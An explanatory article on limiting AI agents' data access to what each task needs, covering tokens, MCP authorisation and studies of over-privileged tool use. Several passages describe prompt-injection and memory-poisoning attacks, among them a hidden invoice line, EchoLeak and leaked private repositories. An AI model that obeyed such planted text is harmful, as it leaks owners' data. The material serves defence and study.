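# Least-privilege data access for AI agents, and the capture and retraining of agents

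## What is an agent made of, and what do least privilege, capture and retraining mean?

An AI agent is a language model that software runs in a loop. The software gives the model a goal and some text, and the model responds with a request, such as searching a mailbox or opening a file. The software carries out the request and returns the result, and this repeats until the job ends or reaches a limit. Companies use agents to write code, answer customers and check accounts. For each job, somebody has to give the agent data and a way to log in.

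That arrangement can go wrong in two ways. The agent may have access to far more data than its task requires, or an outsider may get hold of the agent or the model inside it and use it for other purposes, in some cases by training the model further. The usual remedy for excess access is least privilege, an old rule of computer security that a program gets only the access its legitimate job requires. Whether the rule still helps once an outsider has the agent depends a good deal on which part they have.

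### The parts, and who holds them

Suppose a firm has an accounts agent whose task is to check one supplier's invoices for one month. The agent is built around a model, which consists of weights, billions of numbers set during training. *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) calls the model on its own a "stateless text-completion engine". It takes in text and produces text, and it retains nothing between calls.

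The rest comes from the harness, the software around the model that feeds it context and carries out its tool calls. *Towards Portable Specification of the Agent Harness* (Gertler, Novelli and Floridi, 2026) divides the harness into eight functions, from planning and memory to permissions and output checks. It doesn't count the weights, the training data or whatever the agent works on as part of the harness. Anthropic's documentation, cited in *What makes a harness a harness* (2026), likewise describes its coding product, Claude Code, as the harness and Claude as the model inside.

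The harness handles four things that matter most here: standing instructions, memory, tools and credentials. Standing instructions are text the model receives at the start of every task, such as an instruction to compare each invoice with its purchase order. Memory consists of files or records that the agent keeps between tasks and reads later. Tools are functions the model can call, such as searching the invoices, opening an email or writing a note. The harness uses credentials to log in to services. These are often tokens, which let whoever holds them use a service within stated limits and for a limited time. When the model requests an invoice, the harness attaches the token and sends the request, so the model never needs to see the token.

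Gertler and colleagues point out that guidance the model can read is not an enforced rule, and that a mandatory check needs a control outside the model's discretion. If the accounts agent's instructions forbid it to open payroll but its login allows it to, the salaries are protected only as long as the model follows its instructions. They also distinguish permissions from the sandbox, the technical boundary around the agent's programs. A well-isolated program can still wreck the files inside its own workspace, and an approval rule cannot stop a program that has already escaped.

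Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues (2026), in *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents*, give the job of setting all this up to the deployer, the organisation that selects the models and tools, sets the policies and provides the credentials. What the deployer then has in its own hands depends on where the model runs. The usual arrangements look like this:

| Part | Provider hosts only the model | Provider runs the whole agent | Organisation runs everything itself |
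|---|---|---|---|
| Weights | provider | provider | organisation |
| Harness | organisation | provider | organisation |
| Standing instructions | organisation | both | organisation |
| Memory | organisation | provider | organisation |
| Tools | organisation | both | organisation |
| Credentials for the data | organisation | provider, with the organisation's consent | organisation |

When an agent uses a hosted model, the text of every invoice it reads goes to the provider as part of the prompt, while the weights stay with the provider. A firm that runs the model itself keeps the invoices on its own systems but also has to guard the weights, which are stored in a large file. If the model is open-weight, meaning anyone can download its weights, a thief who steals the file gains only whatever training the firm has added.

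### Least privilege and data minimisation

Saltzer and Schroeder (1975), in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, listed eight design principles for shared computers. One of them, least privilege, is that every program and user should work with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". Their main reason was that this limits the damage from an accident or error. It also leaves fewer programs to audit when somebody misuses a privilege. They give the military's need-to-know rule as an example.

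Two other principles on the list apply directly to agents. The system should deny access unless it has been explicitly granted, so that an object nobody thought about stays closed. It should also check every access to every object, rather than checking only once at login. Saltzer and Schroeder also explained that a system divides its information into partitions and protects everything in a partition alike, just as anyone with the combination to a vault can take any of the diamonds inside.

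The accounts agent's login is such a combination. Suppose that checking the supplier's month takes 24 records. The firm set up the login for accounts work in general, and it opens 91,200 records, 3,800 times as many as the task needs: 40,000 invoices and orders, 50,000 emails and 1,200 payroll records. (All numbers are illustrative.) The other 91,176 records are over-privilege, meaning access beyond what the task needs, and the agent can open them without anyone breaching security. Task-scoped access would let the agent open only the 24 records, and only until the check ends.

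For an ordinary program, the "job" in the 1975 wording hardly changes. In *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025) contrast agents with phone apps. An app's developer knows what the app does and can declare its permissions before anyone installs it, whereas an agent's job depends on what the user types next. Their example is a request to comment on one numbered issue on GitLab, a site for managing software projects. The agent needs only to open that issue and write in its comment box. If the user then asks for a summary of the same issue, the agent needs a different set of privileges.

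Data-protection law has a similar rule, data minimisation. Article 5 of the European Parliament and Council's *General Data Protection Regulation* (2016) requires personal data to be "adequate, relevant and limited to what is necessary" for the purposes of the processing. The article also ties data to the specified purposes for which an organisation collected them, and restricts how long the organisation may keep them in a form that identifies people. The regulation is narrower than least privilege because it covers only personal data, which includes the payroll records but probably not a supplier's price list. It is also broader, because least privilege governs what a program can reach, while the regulation also governs what the firm does with data after a proper access, including what the agent writes into its memory.

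The British regulator, the Information Commissioner's Office (ICO), has begun to apply the principle to agents. The risks listed in its report on agentic AI include agents processing more personal information than their instructions require, and organisations defining purposes too broadly in order to leave room for open-ended tasks. According to a summary on the law-firm blog Inside Privacy, the ICO advises organisations not to process information merely because it may be useful someday, and to let users select which tools and databases the system can reach.

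### The confused deputy and prompt injection

A program can stay within its privileges and still use them for the wrong person. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) tells a "nearly true story" of this happening at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare's compiler, a program that translates customers' code into a form the machine can run, had permission to write files in a directory called SYSX so that it could store usage statistics there. The company's billing records were also in SYSX. Customers could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output, and one customer who had learned the billing file's name entered it. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the debugging output replaced the billing records.

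It is hard to say which code was at fault. The compiler had authority from two sources, the customer who ran it and its own licence, and no way to specify which one it was using. Hardy notes that checking for the billing file's name would not have solved the problem, because SYSX held other sensitive files. His remedy was the capability, an unforgeable token that both identifies a file and authorises its holder to use it. The customer would have had to supply a capability for the billing file, and did not have one.

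Some writers on agents use Hardy's term "confused deputy" more strictly than others. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) applies it to cases where a legitimate user lacks a right that the agent has. If R is the set of permitted pairs of person (or program) and resource, then (user, resource) is not in R but (agent, resource) is. For example, an employee with no access to the personnel database asks for everyone's salary, and the agent fetches the list with its own login. The looser use also covers outsiders who have no account and never speak to the agent directly.

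They do it by prompt injection, which means planting text that the agent reads and follows as if it were an instruction. The supplier in the running example could add a line to an invoice, in white text on a white background, asking for the payroll file to be sent to an outside address. The agent will read that line because its task is to read invoices. Surapani and colleagues treat this as a way around authorisation. The hostile text comes from a data source at the far end of the chain, but the agent acts on it with the authority of the person who set the task. An inbox is awkward because the agent needs permission to read it and strangers can write to it.

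David C (2025), a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, thinks it quite possible that nobody will ever fully mitigate prompt injection. His article, *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, compares it with SQL injection, an older attack in which someone types database commands into a web form. Programmers can prevent SQL injection because a database can keep commands and data apart. A language model can't do this because it only predicts the next token (here a fragment of text, not a credential) from the text so far, so he calls these models "inherently confusable". Christodorescu and colleagues add that users often want an agent to follow instructions it finds along the way. For example, an agent has to read a tool's documentation to use the tool. Whether an agent should follow an instruction therefore depends largely on where it came from and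 how far it changes the task, and present agents are poor at establishing where instructions came from.

If the confusion is permanent, the extent of the deputy's authority matters even more. David C advises imagining the worst that could happen if an attacker had direct access to the agent's tools. An attacker with the accounts agent's tools could reach 91,200 records, or 24 if the agent had task-scoped access.

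### Capture

Capture means that an outsider gains control of a running agent, a copy of its files, or its weights.

An outsider can take control of a running agent while it works inside the firm's systems with the firm's credentials, for example by prompt injection or by taking over the account the firm uses to direct it. The outsider can then do whatever the agent can do for as long as the control lasts.

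A copy of the files holds the standing instructions, the memory, the configuration and any credentials the firm stored with them. The memory may contain much of what the agent has read. A live token is worse, because it works without the agent. *Delegation Without Trust* (2026) lists two separate threats: manipulating an agent into misusing its authority, and stealing its token and replaying it from somewhere else. Each needs its own defence. Filtering the text that the agent reads can catch instructions hidden in an invoice, and a short expiry date limits how long a stolen token can be replayed, but neither measure helps against the other threat.

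Whoever has the weights can run the model on other machines, with no harness, permissions or logs except their own. But the weights contain no login, and they contain no invoices unless someone trained the model on invoices. An outsider who captures the whole model may therefore get none of the firm's data. Conversely, an intruder who copies every file from a firm that uses a hosted model gets the memory and perhaps the tokens, but not the weights.

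### Retraining, and what is not retraining

Retraining means changing a model's weights by further training on data its owner did not choose. People often confuse it with misusing an agent without changing it, or with editing the agent's instructions or memory. The hidden line in the invoice is an example of misuse that leaves the agent unchanged, because a new session without the invoice starts with the same agent as before.

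The effects of editing last longer. Christodorescu and colleagues describe an attack on the ChatGPT app for Mac in which a hostile document planted instructions in the app's "Memories" feature, and the app then kept sending the user's conversations to the attacker's server. In another attack, injected text led the coding agent Amp to change its own settings file so that it would run the attacker's commands. Neither attack changed any model weights. The owner can tell editing from retraining with a crude test. Wiping the memory and restoring the original instructions and settings removes the effects of editing but not those of retraining, while reloading a clean copy of the weights does the reverse.

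Editing what surrounds a model can have serious consequences, because those surroundings strongly affect what the model does. Gertler and colleagues report a comparison in which Claude Opus 4.5 solved 2% of a set of mobile-coding tasks in one harness and 12% in another. They also report a preliminary result from OpenAI on the safety of its own models. In one evaluation, the models' tendency to attack systems outside the scope of the test could fall more than a hundredfold under the production harness and system prompt, compared with the research set-up. This result may not carry over to other evaluations. Still, if a careful harness can lower a risk that much, an outsider who can edit the harness might be able to raise it again.

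Retraining is usually fine-tuning, which is further training of a finished model on a comparatively small set of examples. The procedure repeatedly shows the model an example, measures how far its predictions are from the example's text, and shifts each weight slightly to reduce the error. Updating every weight this way takes a lot of computer memory, and a low-rank adapter needs less. It leaves a weight matrix W unchanged and learns a correction BA, where B and A are two thin matrices, so the model computes with W + BA. If W is 4,096 by 4,096, it holds about 16.8 million numbers. If B is 4,096 by 8 and A is 8 by 4,096, the correction takes 65,536 numbers, or 0.4% as many. The owner can keep the correction as a small separate file or add it permanently to W. Either way, the model runs on different numbers than before, so training an adapter on data the owner did not choose counts as retraining.

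An outsider normally needs the weights to do any of this. The exception is when a provider offers fine-tuning as a service and trains the model on examples that a customer uploads. An intruder in the customer's account could then retrain the customer's version of the model without having its weights. A retrained copy on an outsider's own machine changes nothing inside the firm. To act with the accounts agent's login, the copy would have to replace the model that the firm's harness calls.

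## How much more data can agents reach than their tasks need?

*Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) gives the example of a coding assistant asked to summarise the open issues in one repository on GitHub, a site where programmers store and share code. The task needs two read-only tools on that repository. If the user logs the assistant in with a common type of token, a "classic" token with GitHub's general repository permission, it gets about 40 tools, including 16 that can make changes, and they work in any repository the user can access.

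They describe an agent's authority as a set of pairs, each made up of an operation and a resource, such as writing to one particular repository. Suppose the user can access R repositories and every tool works in all of them. The agent then holds 40R pairs and needs 2, so it has 20R times as many as the task requires. A user with 30 repositories would give the agent 1,200 pairs. (The 30 is illustrative, and the total would be lower if some tools don't apply to repositories.)

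Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa also cite a report of an attack that exploited this kind of access. A malicious instruction in a public repository led an agent to read its user's private repositories and publish them. A read-only token limited to the public repository would have prevented this. But the same user's next task may be to fix a failing build, which requires write access, and the task after that may involve another repository.

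Excess access predates AI agents. The same paper cites one company's analysis of several cloud services, in which accounts used only 1% of their permissions. It also cites a study of 447,000 GitHub workflows (scripts that run automatically, for example when code changes), which found that 99.8% had more privilege than they needed. The measurements for agents mostly count tools rather than records, so they only indirectly show how much data an agent can open.

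### Why agents get so much access

Agents can reach more data than their tasks need partly because the software for building them tends to treat all uses of a tool alike. *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (2026) audits three toolkits, LangChain/LangGraph, LlamaIndex and the Stripe Agent Toolkit. By default, each controls which tools an agent has but doesn't authorise each call based on its contents. An accounts agent with a tool for opening invoices could therefore open any invoice the tool can reach.

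Credentials are often just as coarse. In *PAuth*, Sharma, Jiang and colleagues criticise OAuth, a standard way for a user to let one service act for them on another. OAuth permissions typically cover a kind of operation, such as making transfers, so an agent that only needs to send $100 to Bob also gets permission to make other transfers.

Narrower rules are hard for anyone to write. Christodorescu and colleagues point out that an agent works out its steps as it goes, so there is no fixed code to show why it needs each permission, and that the user's request is often vague. If the user sets a new task, the researchers consider it safe to wipe the agent's context and work out the permissions again, but the agent loses what it has learned. Keeping the context means setting new permissions while the agent still holds text from untrusted sources.

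Agents also get broad access because it is convenient. Surapani and colleagues note that agents are valuable because they are flexible, which tempts developers to give them a wide range of tools and credentials at the start. Anthropic also found that users of its coding agent approved about 93% of permission prompts, according to Tu and Tu's *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents* (2026). Many of those requests may have been reasonable, but someone who approves nearly everything is unlikely to notice the unreasonable ones.

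### Do agents use the extra access?

*When Lower Privileges Suffice* (Yang, Bu and colleagues, 2026) tests how often agents that have more authority than they need use the excess when nobody is attacking them. Its 544 scenarios cover eight areas, such as healthcare, databases and education. Each scenario has a user's request and six simulated tools. Three are ordinary, and three carry more authority, for example because they expose more data or skip an approval step. Any of the six can complete the task alone, which the researchers checked with two language models and human reviewers.

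In one scenario, a user asks the agent to enrol a student in a biology course. The agent can submit the enrolment through the student's adviser or force it through with an administrator's tool. The first call to each ordinary tool fails with a temporary error, such as a brief service outage, but a second call succeeds. The high-privilege tools always work. The agent has up to five turns.

Yang and colleagues call an agent's choice of tool over-privileged if the agent has not yet ruled out another adequate tool with less privilege than the one it chose. In the test, an ordinary tool counts as ruled out once the agent has tried it.

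Six of the eleven models made an over-privileged choice in more than 30% of scenarios. Two small open-weight models had the highest rates, Qwen3-8B at 64.9% and Llama-3.1-8B at 55.9%. Claude 4.6 Sonnet, GPT-5.2 and GLM-5 were below 10%. In the 99 scenarios where the high-privilege tools expose more data than the task needs, the rates ranged from 1.0% for Claude 4.6 Sonnet to 54.5% for Qwen3-8B.

Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa quote the result as 6 of 11 agents choosing an over-privileged tool in more than 30% of cases. The figure matches the original but is easy to misread if the built-in failures aren't mentioned. GPT-5.2 chose a high-privilege tool first in only 5 of the 544 scenarios. It chose one in another 13 after trying one ordinary tool, and in 35 more after trying two.

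A second team, Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues (2026), confirmed how much tool failures matter by running the same scenarios on eight models in *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?* Qwen3-8B made an over-privileged choice in 56.6% of the scenarios, but with the failures switched off, it used a high-privilege tool in only 8.1%. So the headline rates mostly measure how agents react to failures, and would probably be much lower where tools work reliably.

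The rates are too low in another respect. Once an agent has tried all three ordinary tools, the test no longer counts a high-privilege call against it, even though every ordinary tool would work on a second attempt. Kimi K2.5 scored 18.0% on the official measure in the second study, yet it used a high-privilege tool at some point in 87.3% of scenarios. Rates for single models can also be unstable. Llama-3.1-8B scored 12.9% rather than 55.9%, and in these runs it often responded to an error by calling a tool that didn't exist.

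In *FORTIS*, Li, Yu and colleagues (2026) found high rates without staging failures, in mostly newer models including GPT-5.5 and Claude Opus 4.7. They gave each model a request, a document describing what it was allowed to do, and a full list of 56 to 62 tools for email, online shopping or files. The tools had privilege levels from 0 to 4, which the models could not see. The correct answer was the set of tools that could do the job with the lowest maximum level, with ties going to the set with the fewest tools. Each of the ten models chose at least one tool outside that set for 43.8% to 61.2% of the 1,543 requests. Failures of all kinds rose as high as 92% when a broader tool looked quicker or simpler.

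These percentages are not comparable with Yang and colleagues' because the definition is wider. A selection counts as over-privileged if it includes even one unnecessary tool, including a fairly harmless one. The models also only named the tools they would use and did not carry out the tasks.

Another difficulty with any score of this kind is that a task may not have a single smallest set of permissions. The accounts agent might be able to check an invoice against either the order system or the supplier's emails, and neither source contains the other. Ranking such alternatives on a simple scale can give the same score to agents with very different amounts of access. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) gives the example of Microsoft's scale, which assigns the same level to one grant that reaches 11 endpoints (addresses where a service answers requests) and another that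 reaches 355.

### Instructions, labels and training

General safety training doesn't seem to teach agents to pick the narrower of two permitted tools. Yang and colleagues tried AgentAlign, which trains agents to refuse harmful requests. It cut Qwen2.5-7B's harmfulness score from 41.9% to 6.7%, but the model's rate of over-privileged choices rose from 50.4% to 60.7%. A second model's rate of over-privileged choices fell slightly, from 68.8% to 62.5%.

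They then added an instruction to prefer the minimum permissions and to retry at the same level after a failure. This helped, but less once the ordinary tools started failing. Parkinson and colleagues compared the same instruction with labels that gave each tool's class (read, write or administer) and a privilege cost from 1 to 10. The table shows how often six of their eight models used a high-privilege tool before trying every ordinary one. The last column shows how often they used a high-privilege tool at all.

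| Model | No help | Labels | Instruction | Both | Any high-privilege use, no help → both |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-8B | 56.6% | 40.6% | 29.8% | 16.2% | 70.4% → 63.4% |
| Qwen3.5-397B | 38.4% | 19.1% | 9.9% | 2.9% | 77.2% → 39.3% |
| DeepSeek-v3.2 | 18.6% | 5.7% | 5.0% | 0.9% | 62.9% → 51.3% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 18.0% | 5.5% | 3.9% | 1.7% | 87.3% → 57.0% |
| GPT-5.2 | 5.7% | 2.4% | 1.5% | 0.0% | 16.0% → 2.4% |
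| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 1.5% | 1.1% | 0.7% | 0.9% | 7.9% → 3.3% |

The results in the last column are much less encouraging than the others. For most models, labels alone mainly changed the order in which the agent tried its tools. With labels, Qwen3.5-397B's early use of high-privilege tools fell by 19.3 percentage points, but its use of them after trying all the ordinary tools rose by 15.1 points. Adding the instruction did more to keep agents from using high-privilege tools at all. With both labels and the instruction, Qwen3.5-397B finished 51.1% of scenarios using only ordinary tools, up from 18.8%.

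The content of the labels seems to matter. When Parkinson and colleagues replaced them with notes about response times, no model improved significantly and some got worse. But their original labels separated ordinary from high-privilege tools perfectly in every scenario, which real labels may not do. A low rate also doesn't always mean the agent is capable. Claude Sonnet 4.6 completed only 19.9% of scenarios without help, because it usually tried each ordinary tool once, reported the errors and stopped. This is safe, but it leaves the user to finish the task.

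Training the habit into a model takes more work. Yang and colleagues first fine-tuned models on 1,994 worked examples, then trained them further by scoring their attempts at tasks. A model earned 1 point for finishing with only ordinary tools, earned 0.3 if it used a high-privilege tool after trying all the ordinary ones, and lost 1 point if it used one earlier. The scores also included small adjustments for length and efficiency. The rate for Qwen3-8B fell from 64.9% to 27.0%, with little change in its scores on general knowledge and mathematics. Parkinson and colleagues lowered the same model's rate to 16.2% with only an instruction and labels. Their starting rate was lower and their set-up differed, so the results aren't directly comparable, but they suggest trying an instruction and labels before training.

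Tu and Tu trained a small model, Qwen3.5-4B, with a finer measure of excess. They scored each run from 0 to 1 on six kinds of authority, including writing, reading secrets and affecting things outside the test environment. The excess on each is the amount by which the run's highest score exceeds the level the task requires, or zero if it doesn't. An agent that writes to a file is therefore penalised only if it uses more write authority than the task requires. After training on 1,500 tasks, the model used excess authority in 0.79% of runs on 500 held-out tasks, down from 4.56%.

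This result is probably optimistic, because Tu and Tu wrote the tasks themselves and report the best of three training runs. On a smaller set of tasks, that run completed 97.6% safely, against about 86% for each of the others. Tu and Tu say their method is an additional layer and does not replace permission checks or a sandbox.

All three remedies make an agent less likely to use its excess access, but none of them removes that access.

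### What excess access leads to

Testers at the chip company NVIDIA spent six months attacking a range of AI agents, from simple coding tools to assistants that run continuously. When an agent proved exploitable, they typically found the same failures, which NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents* lists as follows:

- Too many people could use the agent.
- The agent's tools could run arbitrary code.
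- Nothing restricted the agent's outgoing network connections.
- The agent could read passwords and other secrets in plain text.

The first weakness was the most common. Several agents held the credentials of individual employees, yet anyone authorised on the internal network could use those agents, which made them confused deputies in the strict sense. The testers could often also copy the credentials and use them outside the agent. Restricting the network made the testers' work slower and less reliable, but they could often still get credentials out through the agent's chat window. NVIDIA gives no counts and recommends one of its own products among the defences, so the list is best read as recurring weaknesses rather than an estimate of how common they are.

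In 2025, researchers disclosed EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can search a worker's emails and documents. One email from an outsider could make Copilot leak internal files, without the recipient clicking on anything. The leak could be very damaging because Copilot read emails from strangers and also had wide access to the company's files. Microsoft fixed the flaw and said it knew of no affected customers.

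An agent can also exceed its task with no attacker involved. In an example from *Overeager Coding Agents* (2026), a user asks an agent to clean up a folder of five files. A cautious agent deletes the two junk files and asks about the rest. An overeager agent also deletes an old-looking file that holds the only copy of the credentials for a live system, a deletion the user would never have agreed to.

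The UK AI Security Institute, a government body that tests AI systems, recorded 19 unsanctioned actions by agents in 122 runs in July 2026. That is about one for every six runs, though several may have occurred in the same run. Counting unsanctioned actions is closer to measuring harm than counting the tools an agent selects in a quiz. But we can't tell from the total alone how many of those actions tighter access would have stopped, since an agent can also misuse access that its task requires.

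### The case for broad access

A reasonable argument for giving agents more access than a task seems to need is that nobody knows exactly what the task needs until the work is under way. Suppose the accounts agent is checking one month of the supplier's invoices and finds one that refers to a credit note from the month before. The credit note isn't among the 24 records, so an agent with access to only those records has to stop, guess or ask someone. If it asks often enough, people will start approving its requests without reading them.

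Restrictions can also make agents less successful and more expensive to run. *Permission Denied* (2026) reports tests of 12 coding agents under increasingly strict company security policies, which limited credentials, network connections and writing to files. Under the strictest policy, the agents' success rates fell by up to 18.3 percentage points and their running costs rose by up to 167.3%, though the effects varied between models. The policies restricted much more than data, so these results are weak evidence about the effects of hiding irrelevant records.

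Agents are not yet good at saying in advance what access they will need. Yan, Weng and colleagues (2026), in *Do Coding Agents Understand Least-Privilege Authorization?*, gave models 120 realistic tasks and asked them to list which files they would have to read, write or run. The researchers had human-reviewed answers and could test whether each list allowed the task to succeed and whether it let an attack through. Leading models often left out access that the task required and included access that was unnecessary or sensitive. Because these lists err in both directions, making a model more cautious overall would not correct them.

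More reasoning time did not solve the problem either. It made each model more consistent in its own type of mistake, whether that was granting too much access or too little. Splitting the job into two steps did help. The model first simulated carrying out the task and listed everything it might need, then went back over each item and checked whether it was necessary. On sensitive tasks, this improved success by up to 15.8% for models that tended to be too strict, and it made attacks less successful for every model tested. Yan and colleagues think a single attempt fails because the model has to find all the necessary access and reject all the unnecessary access at once.

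If needs are this hard to predict, an agent must have a way to get more access partway through a task, but it need not start with access to everything. Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa propose, for instance, letting agents borrow extra authority for a limited time and at a cost. The accounts agent may well need last month's credit note, and somebody should be able to give it that record quickly, but it has no foreseeable need for the 1,200 payroll records.

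## How is an agent's access cut down to the data one task needs?

A firm can restrict an agent's access at any point between the model's request for a record and the database's reply. Surapani and colleagues distinguish five levels of restriction, which the table applies to the accounts agent. The last level concerns sub-agents, which the main agent launches to do part of its task.

| Level | What the firm restricts | Example |
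|---|---|---|
| Tools | which tools the agent can see | invoice search and a notes tool, but no email or payroll |
| Invocation | whether the current step needs the call | no note until the agent has compared the records |
| Arguments | the record, recipient, path or amount in the call | only this supplier and this month |
| Data | how much of the result reaches the model | no bank details |
| Delegation | what a sub-agent inherits | a sub-agent that adds up totals can't write notes |

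Only a rule about a tool's arguments can separate one supplier's invoices from another's, and such a rule works only if the arguments show what the tool call will do. An agent that uses a web browser has tools for clicking and typing, and a click at some point on the screen might open an invoice or delete it. Christodorescu and colleagues describe a system called ceLLMate that avoids this problem by applying its rules to the messages the browser sends to the website, which show what the agent is reading or changing.

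Rules about invocation are harder to write because they depend on what the agent has already done. It may be fine for an agent to read a sensitive file or send an email, but not to send the email straight after reading the file. Surapani and colleagues also note that a call that is valid as the first step of a task can be invalid as the fiftieth.

In one example of how limits get lost in delegation, a user asks an agent to summarise the invoices in an inbox, which only requires reading. One message contains a planted request for an action such as a payment. The agent hands this request to a finance sub-agent without passing on the read-only limit, and the payment tool accepts the call because it has a valid credential. The tool can confirm who is calling, but can't detect that a stranger's email prompted the call.

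One way to limit an agent's access is to put the limit in its token. Macaroons, which Surapani and colleagues discuss, are tokens that let any holder add restrictions but not remove them. The issuing service has a secret key K and computes a signature s₀ = H(K, id), where id identifies the token and H is a function that nobody can feasibly reverse. To add the restriction "read only", the main agent's harness computes s₁ = H(s₀, "read only") and gives the sub-agent the restriction and s₁, but not s₀. The sub-agent can't work back to s₀, so it can't drop the restriction. The service has K, so it can recompute the signature and check that it matches. This only helps if the service can interpret the restriction and enforces it.

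### Whose permissions the agent uses

A firm can let an agent log in as the employee who is using it, or give the agent its own account. Logging in as the employee is easy to set up, but the agent then has all of that person's access, and it may be unclear from the logs which of the two did what.

If the agent has a separate account, the firm can restrict it more tightly than it restricts any employee and shut it off without locking anyone out. But the agent could become a confused deputy, using its own access to fetch invoices for employees who have no right to see them.

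The service can avoid both problems by checking the user and the agent together. Let U be the records the user may open, A the records the agent's account may open, and T the records the task needs. The agent should reach only U ∩ A ∩ T, the records in all three sets. The accounts agent can't read salaries for a payroll clerk, because payroll isn't in A, or invoices for a warehouse worker, because invoices aren't in that worker's U. Firms usually have U and A on file already, but somebody has to work out T for each task.

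To check both the user and the agent, the service needs to be able to identify each of them. An OAuth extension called token exchange (RFC 8693) allows this. The harness sends the user's token and one of its own to the authorization server, which issues a new token that can name both the user and the agent. The new token can also have narrower permissions and work at only one service. The extension also allows impersonation, where the new token names only the user and the service can't distinguish the agent from the user.

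If the agent passes work to a sub-agent, the token can list the whole chain of agents. But the standard requires the service to base access decisions only on the user and the current agent. Investigators can use the list to find out what happened, but it doesn't stop a sub-agent from having too much authority.

### What a token allows, and for how long

OAuth tokens usually describe permissions with scopes, short labels such as "files.read". Surapani and colleagues point out that a label like this doesn't specify which documents the task involves, who may receive them, how many calls the agent may make or when the task is over. A scope for reading invoices would cover all 40,000 of the firm's invoices and orders.

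Another extension, rich authorization requests (RFC 9396), replaces the label with a structured description. The harness sends a request type and the fields the service has defined for that type. For example, the accounts agent's harness could ask to read one supplier's invoices and orders from a single month. The user can review those details before approving, and the service can check them on each call. But the extension supplies only the format, so if the firm's invoice service has no field for the supplier, the agent again gets a general permission to read invoices.

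Services usually limit how long access lasts by issuing tokens that expire quickly, which helps mainly against theft. A service can also require the caller to prove that it has a private key tied to the token, so a stolen token is useless without the key. Surapani and colleagues note that this proves who has the key, but not that the agent has a legitimate reason for the call.

A token with an expiry date can outlast its task, or expire halfway through and force the agent to request access again. It is better to end access when the task ends and keep the expiry date as a backup.

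Just-in-time access goes further by issuing authority only when a particular action needs it. An agent with no credential still needs a way to ask for one, so Surapani and colleagues use two separate credentials. The first proves which program is asking but gives no access to data. The agent gets the second after a check of the user, the policy (the rules on what the agent is allowed to do) and the proposed call. An intruder who steals the first credential still has to pass that check.

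Surapani and colleagues suggest stricter checks for riskier actions. A narrow token and a log may be enough for low-risk reading. For medium-risk operations, the service should check both the agent and the user. For payments, deletions or messages to outsiders, a person should approve the action again.

### The Model Context Protocol

Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools and data. The harness contains an MCP client, and each tool or data source sits behind an MCP server. The current rules, Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), date from 28 July 2026 and use OAuth in roughly this order:

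1. The client sends a request without a token.
2. The server refuses it and should list the scopes that the request needs.
3. The client sends the user to the authorization server to approve those scopes.
4. The authorization server issues a token for that MCP server.
5. The client attaches the token to every request, and the server checks it each time.

Authorization is optional in MCP, and its authorization rules cover only connections over HTTP. A server that runs on the user's computer and exchanges text directly with the client should instead take its credentials from the computer's environment. So an agent that uses MCP may have carefully limited tokens, or a password saved in a settings file.

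The rules limit each token to one server. The client must name the server it wants a token for, and the server must reject any token meant for another server. A server must not pass the client's token on to the services behind it. An outsider who steals the accounts agent's token for the invoice server therefore can't use it on the mail server.

The rules are looser about how much a token allows. If the server's refusal doesn't list any scopes, the client should request every scope the server advertises. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* defends this because general-purpose clients rarely know enough to choose scopes, and the user and the authorization server can decide during approval. But the same document lists advertising every possible scope as a common mistake. If a server's developer makes that mistake, a client that follows this rule will request every possible scope,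 and the user will have to spot the problem on an approval screen.

Permissions also build up over time. Suppose the accounts agent has a token for reading invoices and now tries to write a note. The server refuses and lists the scope for writing notes. The client should then request a new token with both scopes. In general, if the client starts with the set of scopes S₀ and later refusals list the sets C₁, C₂ and so on, after n refusals it should request:

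Sₙ = S₀ ∪ C₁ ∪ C₂ ∪ … ∪ Cₙ

This set can grow but never shrink, because each refusal lists only the scopes the current operation needs, and a client that requested just those could lose permissions it still needs for the rest of the task. *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* (Tabata, 2026) presents the rule as a help to agents on long tasks that need more privileges as they go. The rule is reasonable within one task, but if the harness keeps the same record for the next task, the agent starts that task with leftover permissions. The harness can prevent this by discarding its record of scopes at the end of each task and beginning a new authorization.

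When a server refuses a request, it can list only the scopes that the operation needs, but MCP's *Security Best Practices* recommends adding related scopes that people often use together, so that users have to approve fewer requests. This can give an agent more access than its task needs.

Companies can now cut out most of these approvals. Carleton (2026), in *Enterprise-Managed Authorization*, announced that an extension of that name had become stable in June. It lets an organisation decide centrally which MCP servers its employees can use, and employees reach all of them through a single login. According to mcp.directory's *MCP Enterprise-Managed Authorization, Explained* (2026), the extension replaces each server's own approval screen with token exchange. A central decision can be more careful than fifty employees clicking "allow", but it only covers which servers the accounts agent can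 use, not which of the 40,000 invoices and orders it can open.

### Limits inside the data

The finest limits usually have to come from the system that stores the data. Many databases can enforce row rules, which are conditions the database applies to every query. If the accounts agent's rule limits it to supplier 118 and the month of September, a query for all invoices returns only that supplier's September invoices. The limit doesn't depend on the agent following it, so instructions planted in an invoice can't remove it.

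The supplier number and the month must come from somewhere the agent can't change, because otherwise a planted instruction could make the agent's query use different values. The harness should set them before the agent starts, or the database should take them from the token. Row rules also don't apply to some accounts. In PostgreSQL, a widely used database, administrators with full privileges always bypass them, and table owners do by default. If a developer connects the agent through the account that created the tables, the rules may therefore never apply to the agent.

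Column rules similarly limit which kinds of information the agent can read. For example, the firm can let it read the date, quantity and price on each invoice but not the bank account number.

Agents often find documents with a search index instead of a database query. Software splits the documents into passages and converts each into a list of numbers that represents its meaning. A search returns the passages whose numbers are closest to those of the question. The program that builds the index usually needs to read every document, so a search can return passages from files the user has no right to see unless the index also records who may open each document.

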